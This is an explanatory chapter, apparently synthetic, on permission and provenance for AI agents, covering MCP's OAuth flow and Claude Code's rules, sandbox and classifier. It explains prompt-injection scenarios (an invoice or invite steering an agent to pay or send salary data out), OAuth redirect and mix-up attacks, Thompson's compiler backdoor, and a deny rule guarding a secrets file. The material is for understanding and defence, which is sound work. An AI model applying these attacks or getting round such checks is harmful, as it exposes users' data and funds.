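# Tool authorisation and component provenance for AI systems

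## Permission and origin: the basic ideas

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that carries out the actions the model chooses. The model only produces text. A surrounding program, the host, turns some of that text into operations, such as opening a file, querying a database or sending a message. A tool is any function an agent can call to read or change something outside the model. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, a September 2026 review by Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, cites a count of 177,436 tools in public repositories for a single connection standard, all created between November 2024 and February 2026.

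Tool authorisation means deciding which tool calls may go ahead. Component provenance concerns who made the agent's parts, what they were made from, and whether anyone has altered them since. The two subjects belong together because a part that someone has tampered with acts with whatever permission the agent has.

Suppose a clerk in an accounts department asks an agent to summarise this month's invoices and email the result to the clerk's manager. The agent needs access to a folder of invoices and to the inbox where suppliers send more, as well as the ability to send mail. It also needs credentials, usually an access token, which is a string that the mail service accepts as proof that access has been granted. The clerk's employer set up the agent and gave the token to the host, but most of the rest came from outside the company.

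| Part | What it does in this task | Who typically supplies it |
|---|---|---|
| Model | Reads the invoices and picks the next tool call | An AI company, which trained the weights (the numbers that make up the model) |
| Host | Runs the agent, holds the credentials, executes the calls | A software company, or the employer's own developers |
| Packages | Do routine jobs, such as extracting text from a PDF | Outside programmers, through a public registry (a catalogue for downloads) |
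| Tool server | Connects the host to the mailbox | The mail provider, or a third party |
| Skill | Gives written instructions, often with code, for reading a certain invoice layout | Anyone with an account on a public catalogue |

The clerk has probably never heard of most of these suppliers.

### Who may do what

Much of the vocabulary of permission is about fifty years old. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) defines a principal as the entity to which a computer system grants authorisations, and therefore as the unit of accountability. A clerk, an employer or a program can be a principal.

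They also distinguished authentication, which verifies who is making a request, from authorisation, which grants a principal access to something. People still confuse the two. A valid token from the invoice agent authenticates the agent to the mail service, but it may not establish that the agent is authorised to send this message to this address on the clerk's behalf. Surapani and colleagues stress that an agent can hold a valid token and still lack authority for the particular request it makes.

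A system can record permissions in two ways. An access control list belongs to the protected object and names the principals who may use it. A capability belongs to the user of the object. Saltzer and Schroeder call it an unforgeable ticket, and presenting it proves a right to the object it names. With a list, the invoice folder would carry an entry for the agent, and any request from the agent would pass. With capabilities, the host would give the agent a ticket for this one folder when the task began. The difference becomes important when a program acts for two parties at once.

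Two design rules from the same 1975 paper recur throughout what follows. Least privilege holds that a program should get only the access its task requires. Complete mediation requires the system to check every access, not just the first.

Both are hard to follow with agents. A strictly limited invoice agent could read only one folder and send one message to one address, but the ordinary permission for sending email can't specify a recipient or purpose. Developers also have a reason to grant broad permissions, since an agent is useful largely because nobody has to plan its steps in advance. Surapani and colleagues therefore apply least privilege to several decisions: which tools the agent can see, whether the current step needs the chosen tool, which recipient or file the call names, how much data comes back to the model, and what a helper agent inherits. They want the system to make these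 decisions at each tool call, because a consent screen at the start appears before anyone knows what the calls will be.

### The confused deputy

The classic example of permission going wrong, which involved no break-in, is an incident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Hardy (1988) describes it in *The Confused Deputy* and calls the story "nearly true". Tymshare kept a compiler, a program that translates source code into runnable form, in a directory called SYSX. Any customer could run it and name a file to receive debugging output. Tymshare's programmers later made the compiler collect statistics on how people used the programming language and write them to a file in SYSX. To allow this, they gave it a licence to write any file in that directory, which also held the company's billing records.

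A user learned the name of the billing file and gave it to the compiler as the destination for debugging output. When the compiler tried to open the file, the operating system found that the compiler had a licence to write in SYSX and opened it. The debugging output overwrote the billing records.

Hardy considers and rejects the obvious fixes. The compiler could refuse file names in other directories, but customers had good reasons to send output elsewhere. It could refuse names in SYSX, but some people had legitimate access there, and the directory's name did not exist when the programmers wrote the code. It could refuse the billing file by name, but someone would have to amend the compiler for each new sensitive file. Hardy concludes that the compiler had authority from two sources, the customer and Tymshare, and no way to express which one it was using for a given write. He therefore calls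 it a confused deputy, meaning a program that someone can trick into using its own authority on behalf of a person who lacks it.

Tymshare first added a system call that let a program "switch hats" between its two authorities, but some programs soon needed more than two. Hardy came to prefer using capabilities. Tymshare would give the compiler a capability for the statistics file, and the customer would supply one for the output file. Each capability both identifies a file and authorises writing to it, so a customer without one for the billing file could not get the compiler to overwrite that file just by naming it.

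Prompt injection recreates the same situation in an agent. The term covers text, in material an agent reads, that makes it follow instructions its user did not give. Surapani and colleagues describe a case very close to the clerk's. A user authorises an agent to summarise invoices from an inbox, and one message contains an instruction to make a payment or forward data. The agent passes that request to a second agent that handles finance, but does not pass on the limit to reading. The payment tool receives a valid credential and executes the call. The service at the far end can confirm who called it, but it cannot discover that a stranger's email prompted the call.

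This is the Tymshare problem again, with an email in place of a file name, but the remedy carries over less well. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 article from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C compares prompt injection with SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can prevent SQL injection completely, because a database engine handles commands and data differently and a properly written query keeps them apart. A language model has a single stream of text and predicts what comes next. Developers can mark some of the text as data, or train the model to give its user's instructions more weight. Both measures lower the odds of a successful attack, but neither creates a boundary between instructions and data. He concludes that a model is an "inherently confusable deputy" and that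 prompt injection may never have a full fix.

Hardy's compiler wrote files at two separate places in its code, and a programmer could attach the right ticket to each, but a model has no such places. Capabilities still help, since an invoice agent that holds a ticket for one recipient cannot write to another, whatever it reads. But they do not prevent hidden text in an invoice from changing the total in the summary that the manager receives.

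David C recommends a rule that came out of an exchange between the programmers Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: while a model processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to those of that party. Under this severe rule, an agent that reads the inbox should have no tool that its owner would refuse to a random outsider, because anyone can email an invoice. In the clerk's case, ordinary code with a fixed address would send mail instead of the model. This makes the agent less flexible, and much of the argument about agent security is about whether designers can avoid that loss.

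### Where a component came from

We have assumed so far that the host, the packages and the tool server are what their makers released. OpenSSF (2024), the Open Source Security Foundation, points out that people who run software usually have no strong guarantee of this, because the history of the file, from source code to finished program, is lost or unclear. Four devices recover parts of that history, and we need to be exact about how much each one proves.

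A hash is a short value computed from a file. With the hash functions that NIST, the US standards agency, approves, nobody can feasibly build a file to fit a given hash or find two files with the same hash, and almost any change to a file changes its hash. If the employer has the correct hash for a package and the downloaded copy produces the same value, the copy is that package, byte for byte. But the employer may have the wrong hash, because an attacker who can replace a file on a website can often replace the hash printed next to it.

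A signature shows that the holder of a particular key approved a file's exact bytes. The maker signs the file with a private key and publishes a matching public key, which anyone can use to check the signature. NIST's *Digital Signature Standard (DSS)* adds that the recipient can show the signature to a third party as evidence, so the signer cannot easily deny it later. However, a thief who has the private key can produce equally valid signatures, and a harmful program signed by its real author will also pass the check.

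A bare signature also doesn't specify what it means. The signer may have made the file, tested it, or only approved it for release. *Software attestations*, part of the industry specification Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts (SLSA), notes that the signer and recipient must agree on the meaning beforehand and need a new set of keys for each additional meaning. An attestation makes the meaning explicit because it is a signed statement with a subject (the component, usually identified by its hash) and a predicate (what the signer states about it).

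Provenance is a record of who made a component, from what inputs and by what process. It often takes the form of an attestation, a statement that a package with a given hash was built from particular source code, by a particular build command, using particular other packages. A successful check proves that a certain build service made that statement about that exact package. It doesn't prove that the statement is true, which depends on the build service, or that the source code is good. GitHub's *Artifact attestations*, the documentation for one widely used version, warns that an attestation doesn't guarantee security.

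Two cases from SLSA illustrate the limits of provenance. In one, an attacker used leaked credentials to place a malicious file where Codecov's customers downloaded its software. Provenance would have exposed the swap, because the file had not come from the expected source by the expected route. In the other, the makers of SpySheriff sold malicious software as protection against spyware. Accurate provenance would have traced the program to its makers without revealing that they meant to do harm.

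### Why reading the source is not enough

A buyer cannot close that last gap by reading the source code. Ken Thompson, one of the creators of the Unix operating system, showed why in his Turing Award lecture, *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (Thompson, 1984). He built his demonstration in three stages.

The first is that a program can output its own source code and carry any amount of extra material along with it. The second concerns a compiler written in the language it compiles. Suppose its developers want it to recognise a new symbol for the vertical tab. They write the character's number, 11, into the source once and compile. They can then replace the number in the source with the symbol itself, because the compiled program already contains the number. A compiler can thus hold information that appears nowhere in its source.

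Thompson then used this for harm. He altered the C compiler so that, whenever it compiled the Unix login program, it added a second password known to him. Anyone who read the compiler's source would have noticed the change, so he added another, which detected when the compiler's own source was being compiled and reinserted both changes. After compiling this version once and installing it, he could delete every trace from the source. The clean source now produced a corrupt compiler, which produced a corrupt login program, and someone reading the source of both programs would find nothing wrong. Thompson concluded that "no amount of source-level verification or scrutiny will protect you" from code you have no reason to trust.

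A provenance record would not expose the attack either, because it would accurately state that the login program was built from the published source with the official compiler.

David A. Wheeler proposed a partial answer in a later doctoral dissertation. The tester builds the suspect compiler's source with a second, unrelated compiler, uses the result to build the source again, and compares this second build with the suspect program bit by bit. A mismatch reveals the corruption. The test requires a second compiler that does not share the fault and builds that are identical every time.

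People disagree about what to trust. In the subtitle of his lecture, Thompson suggested that it may matter more to trust the people who wrote the software. SLSA's guiding principle is nearly the opposite, "Trust code, not individuals", because people make mistakes and lose their passwords, whereas code is static and can be inspected. SLSA acknowledges that everyone has to trust some platform, and proposes examining a few build services closely and checking their many products automatically. This seems the only workable approach for ordinary packages, since no employer can vet thousands of programmers, but it makes the build service the obvious target. In the SolarWinds case, which SLSA also lists, attackers compromised the build platform and added malicious behaviour during each build without changing the source. Model weights are even harder to check because they have no human-readable source.

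### The chain from user to tool

Permission and origin meet when an agent makes a call, and by then several parties stand behind it. Surapani and colleagues arrange them in five layers, numbered from zero:

- Layer 0 is the human user, here the clerk, from whom legitimate authority comes.
- Layer 1 is the operator, the organisation that configures the agent, sets its policies and provides its credentials. The clerk's employer can forbid things that the clerk asks for.
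- Layer 2 is the main agent, or orchestrator, which breaks the task into steps.
- Layer 3 holds any sub-agents, such as one that only extracts figures from PDFs.
- Layer 4 is the tool endpoint: the mailbox, the file store, the payment service.

Authority should only narrow as it passes down from one layer to the next. A sub-agent that extracts figures, for example, does not need permission to send mail. The bottom layer is awkward because a resource there, such as a mailbox, is both something the agent needs permission to use and a source of text from strangers. A sound decision therefore draws on a record of who passed authority to whom and a record of where the text behind the request came from.

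The review uses one example to show how this would work. A user asks a calendar assistant to summarise the week's meetings, and the system grants permission only to read that week's calendar. One invitation contains a line asking the assistant to send salary information to an outside address. The system labels the invitation's text as untrusted when it arrives. When the assistant proposes to look up the salary, the system refuses because the personnel database lies outside the task and the request derives from untrusted text. It refuses the outgoing email for similar reasons. Neither refusal requires the system to recognise the line as an attack. The system records both decisions and lets the user confirm the refusal or approve the action once.

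What a check can catch depends on where it runs. A check at the mail service can use only the valid token and the outside recipient, so it must either block all outside mail or let this message through. A check inside the host can detect that the idea of sending the message came from an invitation, but a sub-agent can bypass it by calling the mail tool through another route. Surapani and colleagues want both checks. Their trace is a worked example on paper, and they found no standard that requires any such check on every call.

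They also rated ten families of existing mechanisms against seven requirements. The mechanisms did worst at limiting what an agent can work out by combining several sources, each of which it may read. No family offered more than partial help with this. Simple accountability is also weak. In a 2026 survey they cite, from the Cloud Security Alliance and the company Strata, only 28% of organisations could trace their agents' actions back to a responsible human in all their systems. The reviewers treat such industry surveys as indicative only, but the result would be worrying even if the true figure were moderately higher.

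A tool's origin matters to permission because a model learns what the tool does from a description written by its supplier. If the supplier changes the description or the code behind it, an agent can become able to do more even though the employer has installed nothing new. The reviewers would tie each permission to a particular version of a tool, a hash of its description and the registry it came from, and reconsider the permission when any of these changes.

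Four questions help distinguish one system, or one failure, from another. The first is who granted the authority, which could be the user, the operator, or nobody in particular, because a broad token was already available. The second is what was checked, such as an identity, a permission for this action, the bytes of a file, or the record of how someone built it. The third is when the check took place, whether at installation, at a consent screen, or at each call. The fourth is who carried it out, which could be a person, the host, a registry, the remote service, or the same model that had just read an email from a stranger.

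## The Model Context Protocol: how an agent obtains access to a tool

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard for connecting agents to tools and data. Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, published it in November 2024. The Model Context Protocol blog later announced that Anthropic had donated it to the Agentic AI Foundation, a body under the Linux Foundation. A mail provider, for example, can write a single MCP server that works with every agent whose host supports the standard, instead of a separate connector for each. The maintainers counted close to half a billion downloads a month of their main developer kits when they released the current specification on 28 July 2026 (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

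The host contains a client, which communicates with MCP servers. The client requests a list of tools from a server. Each entry has a name, a description in ordinary language, and a schema that formally specifies the arguments the tool takes. The model reads the list, picks a tool and fills in the arguments. The client then sends the call to the server, which runs the tool and returns the result.

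A local server is a program on the user's own machine. The host starts it and exchanges text with it through its standard input and output (stdio). A remote server is a web service that the client reaches over HTTP. The authorisation flow covers only remote servers.

### How the rules changed

The first version of MCP did not require authentication for remote servers, since developers mostly used the protocol to connect programs on one machine. *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (Zhou, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) traces the next three revisions. In March 2025 MCP adopted OAuth 2.1, a version of the web's usual method for letting one program use another on a person's behalf. The June 2025 revision gave servers a standard way to announce who issues their tokens, and required each server to check that the tokens it received were meant for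 it. In November 2025 the maintainers began to prefer that clients identify themselves with a document their maker publishes on the web, rather than through dynamic client registration, in which any program can sign itself up. According to the Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026), the July 2026 revision makes clients check who sent an authorisation response and ties a client's credentials to the authorisation server that issued them. It also deprecates dynamic registration, which still works for now.

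*Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* (Tabata, 2026) points out that OAuth deployments had used all the July measures for years. MCP began as a convenience for developers and has been adopting older web practices.

### From a refused request to a token

OAuth adds one more party, the authorisation server, which logs the user in, requests consent and issues access tokens. It may belong to the company that runs the MCP server or to another company. The Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* specification sets out the steps, and the protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* describes most of the attacks those steps guard against. Suppose the clerk's employer keeps its invoices in a file store behind a remote MCP server, and the clerk's agent connects to that server for the first time.

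The client sends its first request without a token, and the server rejects it with the code 401, which means that authorisation is missing or invalid. This keeps out anonymous callers. The response also contains the address of a metadata document and, if the server follows the recommendation, the scope that the client needs, here `files:read`. Naming the scope guards against excessive permissions, because otherwise the client requests every scope on the server's published list. That list is supposed to be minimal, but the server's developers decide how long it is.

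The client next chooses an authorisation server from the one or more listed in the metadata document, downloads its description and stores its identifier, called the issuer. The client later uses the issuer to prevent a mix-up attack, in which an attacker who controls one of the agent's authorisation servers tries to make the client send that server a login code issued by an honest one. A Model Context Protocol (2026) post from May notes that these attacks are more prevalent when one client talks to many servers, which is how people use MCP.

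The client then identifies itself to the authorisation server, preferably with a web address. The server downloads a short document from that address, listing the client's name and its redirect addresses, where the browser may deliver the result of the login. The server must accept a redirect address only if it exactly matches one in the document. Otherwise an attacker could send the clerk a login link containing the attacker's own address and collect the result, an attack known as open redirection. The method is weaker for desktop programs because they receive the result at `localhost`, an address that means "this computer", where a hostile program on the same machine can pose as the real client. The authorisation server must therefore show the user the redirect address's hostname, and should add a warning when the only address is `localhost`.

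The client then opens a browser, where the clerk logs in and approves or refuses. This consent guards against a version of Hardy's confused deputy. Some MCP servers are go-betweens that use another company's service under one fixed identifier. That company can't distinguish between the clients behind the go-between, so a stranger's client could use an approval the clerk gave for a different one. The go-between must therefore get the clerk's consent separately for each client that registered itself. In a large firm, however, the clerk may never see a consent screen, because an extension that became stable in 2026 lets an organisation grant access to MCP servers through its own login system. The operator then supplies the authority, and the user finds the servers already connected.

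If the clerk approves, the authorisation server sends the browser back to the client with a short code. The server sends the token later, because another program may intercept anything that passes through the browser. PKCE (Proof Key for Code Exchange) makes a stolen code useless. Before opening the browser, the client generated a random secret, and it sent the server only a hash of that secret. To exchange the code for a token, the client must send the secret, and the server checks that it matches the hash. A client must refuse to continue with any authorisation server that does not advertise support for PKCE.

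Before it sends the code anywhere, the client also compares the issuer named in the response with the one it stored, and stops if they differ. But if an authorisation server neither includes its issuer in its responses nor advertises that it does, the client has nothing to compare, so it proceeds. The maintainers expect to make including the issuer compulsory in a later revision.

The last step produces a token for one server. The client names the MCP server it wants to use in both of its requests to the authorisation server, and the MCP server must reject any token meant for a different one. Without this check, a malicious server could take the token an agent sent it and use it at the clerk's mail provider. The MCP server also must not forward the token to services behind it, and needs a separate token for those. Restricting a token to one server works fully only where the authorisation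 server supports it.

The token resembles the ticket that Saltzer and Schroeder called a capability, but it is less specific. It names a server and some broad scopes, whereas a true capability would name a single file. Anyone who steals the token can use it, so authorisation servers should issue tokens that expire quickly.

### Asking for more access

The clerk's agent holds a token with `files:read`. It reads the invoices and then tries to save its summary in the same store. The server finds no permission to write and replies:

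```
HTTP/1.1 403 Forbidden
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer error="insufficient_scope", scope="files:write"
```

A 403 response here means that the token is valid but does not permit this operation. The client should then request the additional permission, a procedure called step-up authorisation.

The client could ask for `files:write` alone. The new token would then allow writing but not reading, and reading the next invoice would fail with another 403, this time for lack of `files:read`. The agent would keep alternating between the two scopes, returning to the authorisation server each time. To avoid this, the July specification has the client request every scope it has requested before, plus those listed in the latest refusal. Once the clerk approves, the client receives a token with both scopes and repeats the failed call.

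Suppose the agent later has to delete an old draft, and that this server has a third scope for deletion:

| What the agent tries | Scope in the refusal | Scopes the client requests |
|---|---|---|
| Read an invoice, with no token | `files:read` | `files:read` |
| Save the summary | `files:write` | `files:read`, `files:write` |
| Delete an old draft | `files:delete` | `files:read`, `files:write`, `files:delete` |

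The rule takes a union of scopes, so the set never shrinks. Once the draft is gone, no step in the flow removes `files:delete`, and the agent can keep deleting files for as long as it can renew its access. The union also includes scopes the client requested but did not receive, so a permission the clerk once declined may well appear again on the next consent screen.

The November 2025 text of the Model Context Protocol instead let servers choose whether to list only the new scopes, include the existing ones, or add related scopes that are often used together. The July rule is more predictable. It is also a reasonable trade-off for a ten-minute task, since people who see a consent screen every few minutes stop reading it. It is much less suitable for long-running agents. Tabata observes that agents may continue long after the user's initial involvement, and the July revision also explains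 how clients can request refresh tokens, which renew access without the user. An agent that works this way for a month can end up with every permission it needed on any day of that month, which is close to the opposite of least privilege.

Under the specification, servers should ask for all the scopes an operation needs together, and clients should retry only a few times before treating the refusal as permanent. An agent that acts on its own behalf, with no user to consult, may give up.

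### How many servers follow the flow

Authorisation is optional in the July specification, as it was in the previous June's (Model Context Protocol, 2025). Even a remote server that supports authorisation "should" follow the flow but is not required to. Two groups of measurements from 2026 give some idea of how many servers do.

Zhou and colleagues searched FOFA and Shodan, two search engines for machines connected to the internet, for traces typical of MCP and found 28,715 candidate addresses. They sent each one MCP's opening message and kept the 7,973 that gave a valid reply. Two researchers checked a random 100 of these by hand and found one that was not an MCP server. Of the 7,973, 40.55% exposed their tools without authentication, 29.00% used a fixed token or key, and 30.45% used OAuth.

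The first figure is probably less serious than it sounds. The researchers examined a random sample of the open servers, and most seemed to be tests or demonstrations that exposed nothing sensitive. But one belonged to a customer-management system intended for internal use. Anyone who connected could query more than 5,000 records containing names, phone numbers and home or business addresses.

They then looked at the 2,428 servers that did use OAuth, and selected the 1,118 that advertised dynamic client registration because they couldn't automate the test for the rest. They removed duplicates, broken servers, servers that needed no login, and 316 behind strict company access controls. All 119 remaining servers had at least one flaw. The researchers report 325 flaws in total, although their counts by type add up to 335.

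The most common flaw, found in 114 of the 119 servers, was a registration service that let anyone anonymously register a client with any redirect address. An attacker can then send a victim a link to the real login page. If the victim approves, the authorisation code goes to the attacker. PKCE does not prevent this, because the attacker started the process and holds the matching secret. The victim's best chance is to notice an unfamiliar address on the consent screen, but 72 servers did not display the address. Some of these servers were also among the 81 that did not properly enforce PKCE.

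Every tested server offered dynamic registration, the feature that produced the most common flaw, and the selection excluded companies with strict controls, so the sample can't show that OAuth is broken on all MCP servers. The result does strongly support the July decision to deprecate dynamic registration. An attacker can publish a client document too, but it has to sit at a web address that an authorisation server can show to the user or block.

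The second study, *Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026), is an audit by a single researcher. Padilla drew on eleven sources, including code-hosting sites, package registries and catalogues of MCP servers, and ran four scans in July 2026. He confirmed 640 servers, actively tested 414 of them, and reported that 91.8% of those tested lacked OAuth. That is more than double the 40.55% in the earlier study, but the two percentages measure different things.

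| | Zhou and colleagues | Padilla |
|---|---|---|
| Live servers found | 7,973 | 640 across four scans |
| No OAuth | 69.55% | 91.8% of the 414 audited |
| No credential of any kind | 40.55% | 106 of 464 in one scan, or 23% |

A server without OAuth may still require a key, so Padilla mistakenly calls the 91.8% "unauthenticated" at one point. The fair comparison is with the 69.55% of servers in the earlier study that used either a fixed key or no credentials.

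Much of the remaining gap probably comes from which servers the audit included. Padilla's scanner excluded servers that answered its opening message with an authentication error. Servers that follow the MCP flow give that answer, so the audit left out many of those doing what the specification recommends. His sources also included platforms where people post experiments. Of the 464 servers he confirmed on 21 July, 193 had disappeared three days later.

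The most important question is whether a stranger can use the tools with no credential, and Padilla's figure for this is the lower of the two. He counted servers where a direct tool call required no credential, whereas Zhou and colleagues appear to have classified most servers from their response to an opening handshake. Some servers may show their tools to anyone but require a key to call them. The true share of open servers is uncertain and changes from week to week, but either estimate is high for services that can act on private data. Across the 640 servers, Padilla also counted 687 tools that required no credential and whose names and descriptions indicated that they run commands on the server's machine.

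Padilla blames missing authentication on defaults more than on carelessness. MCP's designers started with local servers, where the operating system keeps strangers out, and added HTTP later. He says the standard starter command still produces a web server without authentication. He wants the developer kits to enable OAuth by default, which seems more likely to work than urging thousands of hobbyists to read the specification.

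### What a token leaves undecided

The specification deliberately omits this flow for local servers, which should instead take their credentials from the environment, meaning the settings a program receives when it starts, such as an access key for a mail account. There is no 401, scope or consent screen. A local server runs under the user's identity and can read any file the user can, unless something else restricts it. This is convenient, but dangerous if the server is malicious. Neither study covers local servers, because nobody can scan them from outside, and Padilla thinks they may be the majority.

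Even when the remote flow is carried out perfectly, a valid token does not guarantee a legitimate request. With `files:read` and `files:write`, the clerk's agent can save a summary or, if it follows hidden instructions in an invoice, overwrite any of last year's accounts that the clerk can access. Both calls pass every check on the token, although they differ in their arguments and in whether they match what the clerk asked for.

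The July revision helps a little. Each remote call must now name the tool in an HTTP header, and servers reject calls where the header and the message don't match. A gateway, which is a checkpoint between clients and servers, can therefore block a given tool without reading the message. But the arguments, which determine whether a call saves a summary or destroys the accounts, generally stay in the message body.

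A draft standard from the OpenID Foundation, which maintains widely used login standards, would check those arguments. *AuthZen Profile for Model Context Protocol Tool Authorization* (Tulshibagwale and Olivier, 2026) proposes that each tool's entry in the server's list include a mapping that specifies how to turn a call into a question with four parts: who is asking (the subject), what they want to do (the action), to what (the resource), and in what circumstances (the context). A gateway or the MCP server would fill in the question for each call and send it to a policy service, which returns yes or no.

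In the main example, an agent working for Alice calls a tool named `get_customer` with a customer number and a case number. The subject is Alice, identified from her token, the action is the tool's name, and the resource is that customer. The context contains the agent's identifier and the case. An employer could write a policy that lets Alice's agent open this record only while she is assigned to this case, which no ordinary scope can express. A tool that copies a file requires two checks, one for reading the source and one for writing to the destination, and both must pass. A money transfer above 10,000 can carry a label that triggers a stricter policy. If the policy service refuses or is unreachable, the tool must not run.

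A policy could allow the clerk's agent to write only to the summaries folder. The gateway would then block the attack on last year's accounts, whatever instructions the invoice contained.

A companion draft covers requests that cannot be allowed yet (OpenID Foundation, 2026). In its example, an agent tries to pay a supplier more than a set limit, and the policy service replies that the payment needs approval. After a manager approves it through the company's usual process, the service decides again, and the agent never treats the manager's approval itself as permission to pay.

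The Foundation's working group adopted both documents as official drafts in June 2026. *Getting Cozy with COAZ* (Tulshibagwale and Olivier, 2026) reports that by the end of July the group had split the MCP profile into a general framework and a part specific to MCP. The new version supplies a default mapping for every type of MCP message, so a gateway can check a tool even if its developer wrote no mapping. Both parts were still early drafts, and the Foundation as a whole was some way from ratifying a version for implementers.

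The design has two weaknesses. First, if no gateway or server on the route reads the mapping, it has no effect and access falls back to scopes. Second, the tool's supplier writes any custom mapping. The February draft asks gateways to check that a mapping is well formed, but a dishonest supplier could write a well-formed mapping that omits the argument that matters.

A further difficulty is that the model fills in the case number, whereas Alice's name comes from a signed token. A policy service with access to the firm's records can check that the case exists, that it concerns this customer and that Alice is assigned to it, but it has no record of what she asked her agent to do. If an email with hidden instructions leads the agent to open another of Alice's cases, the call will pass all three checks. To refuse it, a system would have to derive the agent's permissions from the request Alice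 typed, as CaMeL, Progent and related research designs aim to do.

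## Claude Code: who approves each action

Claude Code is Anthropic's coding agent. A programmer starts it in a project folder and describes a task, and the agent reads files, edits them and runs programs until it has finished. It does much of this work through a shell tool called Bash, which runs any command the programmer could type. No access token limits these commands, because they run on the programmer's machine with the programmer's privileges. The host therefore has to decide whether to allow each action.

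Claude Code has four controls: written rules, prompts to the user, a sandbox, and a second model that reviews actions in the user's place. The last, called auto mode, first became a default setting in August 2026.

### Rules, prompts and the sandbox

A permission rule names a tool and usually adds a pattern. `Bash(npm test)` covers only the command `npm test`, which runs a project's tests. `Bash(git push *)` covers commands that begin with `git push`, which send code to a shared repository. A rule can allow the action, deny it, or make Claude Code ask the user. According to Anthropic's documentation, Claude Code checks deny rules first, then ask rules, then allow rules, and applies the first rule that matches. A narrow allow rule therefore cannot make an exception to a broad deny rule.

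Claude Code enforces these rules itself rather than relying on the model to obey them. Writing "never push" in the project's instruction file influences what the model attempts, whereas a deny rule stops the call. But a command rule only compares text, so a differently worded command can still run the same program. Anthropic warns that such a rule is not a security boundary around the program.

A project downloaded from a stranger may contain a settings file with its own allow rules. In an interactive session, Claude Code applies these rules only after the user accepts a dialog that lists them. Deny and ask rules in the file don't need this consent because they can only restrict the agent.

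In Manual mode, Claude Code asks the user to approve most file edits, commands and network requests that no rule already allows or blocks. A typical prompt shows the command and offers four answers: yes, yes and don't ask again for commands like this, yes and switch to auto mode, or no. The second answer saves a permanent allow rule for the whole repository. Permissions can accumulate this way, much as scopes do in MCP's step-up procedure.

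The sandbox limits what a running command can reach, and the operating system enforces those limits. Anthropic says that, by default, a sandboxed command can write only to the working folder, a temporary folder and any folders the user has added. It cannot contact a new internet domain without approval. Anthropic considers both limits necessary, since an agent with free network access could send private files to an attacker.

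According to Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool*, sandboxed commands can read almost the whole computer, including stored credentials, unless the user blocks those folders. The sandbox covers only shell commands and the programs they start, so the agent's built-in file tools and any local MCP servers run outside it.

### A second model as reviewer

Auto mode appeared in March 2026, at first only on Team plans and with an administrator's approval, according to Help Net Security's *Anthropic trims action approval loop, lets Claude Code make the call* (2026). Before then, users who were tired of prompts could either configure the sandbox, which takes some effort, or bypass the prompts altogether.

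In auto mode, a separate model called the classifier judges actions before they run (Anthropic, *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, 2026). The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. It does not receive the agent's own explanations, which might persuade it to approve something dangerous, or the results of tool calls, which could contain a stranger's instructions. A separate check scans those results and warns the agent about any text that resembles prompt injection.

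This partly solves the problem of Alice's agent and the wrong case file. The policy service had no record of what Alice had asked for, but such a classifier would have her words. It would still lack the other record that Surapani and colleagues want, which shows where the text behind a request came from. If an agent tries to cancel job abc123, which the user never mentioned, the classifier cannot determine whether the agent found that ID in a list or made it up. Anthropic accepted this limitation in exchange for protection against injected text.

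The classifier's instructions treat anything the agent chose for itself as unauthorised until the user says otherwise. "Clean up my branches", for example, does not authorise a mass deletion. A user can clear many blocks by giving specific permission in the conversation. To permit a force push, which overwrites the shared history of a project, the user must name the branch.

Users can also state limits, such as "don't push". Anthropic notes that the classifier rereads these limits from the conversation at every check, so a limit can be lost when Claude Code compresses a long session. Only a deny rule guarantees that a limit stays in force.

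When the main agent delegates a task, its instruction takes the place of the user's message within the sub-agent, so any task would appear authorised. The classifier therefore reviews the assignment before the sub-agent starts, then each of its actions, and finally its report.

### One command from proposal to execution

Suppose a developer maintains the software that processes the clerk's invoices. Her settings deny access to `.env`, a file that often holds passwords, and require a prompt before `git push`. They allow `npm test` and every command that starts with `python`, through the rule `Bash(python *)`. She asks the agent to fix a script that miscalculates totals. The agent edits the script and proposes to run `python total.py`.

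Claude Code finds no matching deny or ask rule. In Manual mode, it then finds the allow rule for Python and runs the script without a prompt. In auto mode, it doesn't use that rule because it set the rule aside when the mode began. A Python script can do nearly anything the user can, so if the rule stayed active, the classifier would never receive the commands most capable of causing damage. Claude Code also sets aside rules that allow every shell command, and it restores all these rules when the user leaves auto mode. Narrow rules such as the one for `npm test` stay in force. Anthropic admits that its list of overly broad rules will never be complete.

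Claude Code next applies its built-in exemptions, which normally let the agent read files and edit most files in the project without review, since version control makes such edits easy to inspect. Running a script is not exempt, so the command goes to the classifier.

The classifier first makes a quick yes-or-no decision, under instructions to block when in doubt. If it flags the command, it reviews the same material again with step-by-step reasoning. When a command runs a script the agent has just written, the classifier checks the script's contents as well as the command.

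If the classifier approves, the script runs, and if the developer has turned on the sandbox, it runs inside it. If the classifier refuses, the agent receives a reason and looks for a safer way to finish the task. After three refusals in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user.

| Proposed action | Manual mode | Auto mode |
|---|---|---|
| Read `.env` | Deny rule blocks it | Deny rule blocks it |
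| Edit `total.py` | User decides | Runs |
| `npm test` | Runs under the allow rule | Runs under the allow rule |
| `python total.py` | Runs under the allow rule | Classifier decides |
| `git push` | User decides | User decides |
| `terraform destroy`, which tears down servers | User decides | Classifier decides, and blocks it by default |

Auto mode is thus stricter than Manual mode for this developer's Python commands, and looser for her file edits.

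### Do people read the prompts?

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts. Anthropic had reported 93% in March. A quarter of interactive sessions started with prompts bypassed, and by June almost half of active terminal users had written an allow rule for shell commands.

A high approval rate does not prove that users are careless, because most requests are harmless. The same users reject 39% of the plans the agent submits before starting work, so they evidently read some of what it shows them.

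To test attention directly, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor to work in an environment built for the study. The testers knew they were being evaluated in a coding study, but not on what. Partway through each session, one prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. Nothing dangerous ran even if the tester approved it.

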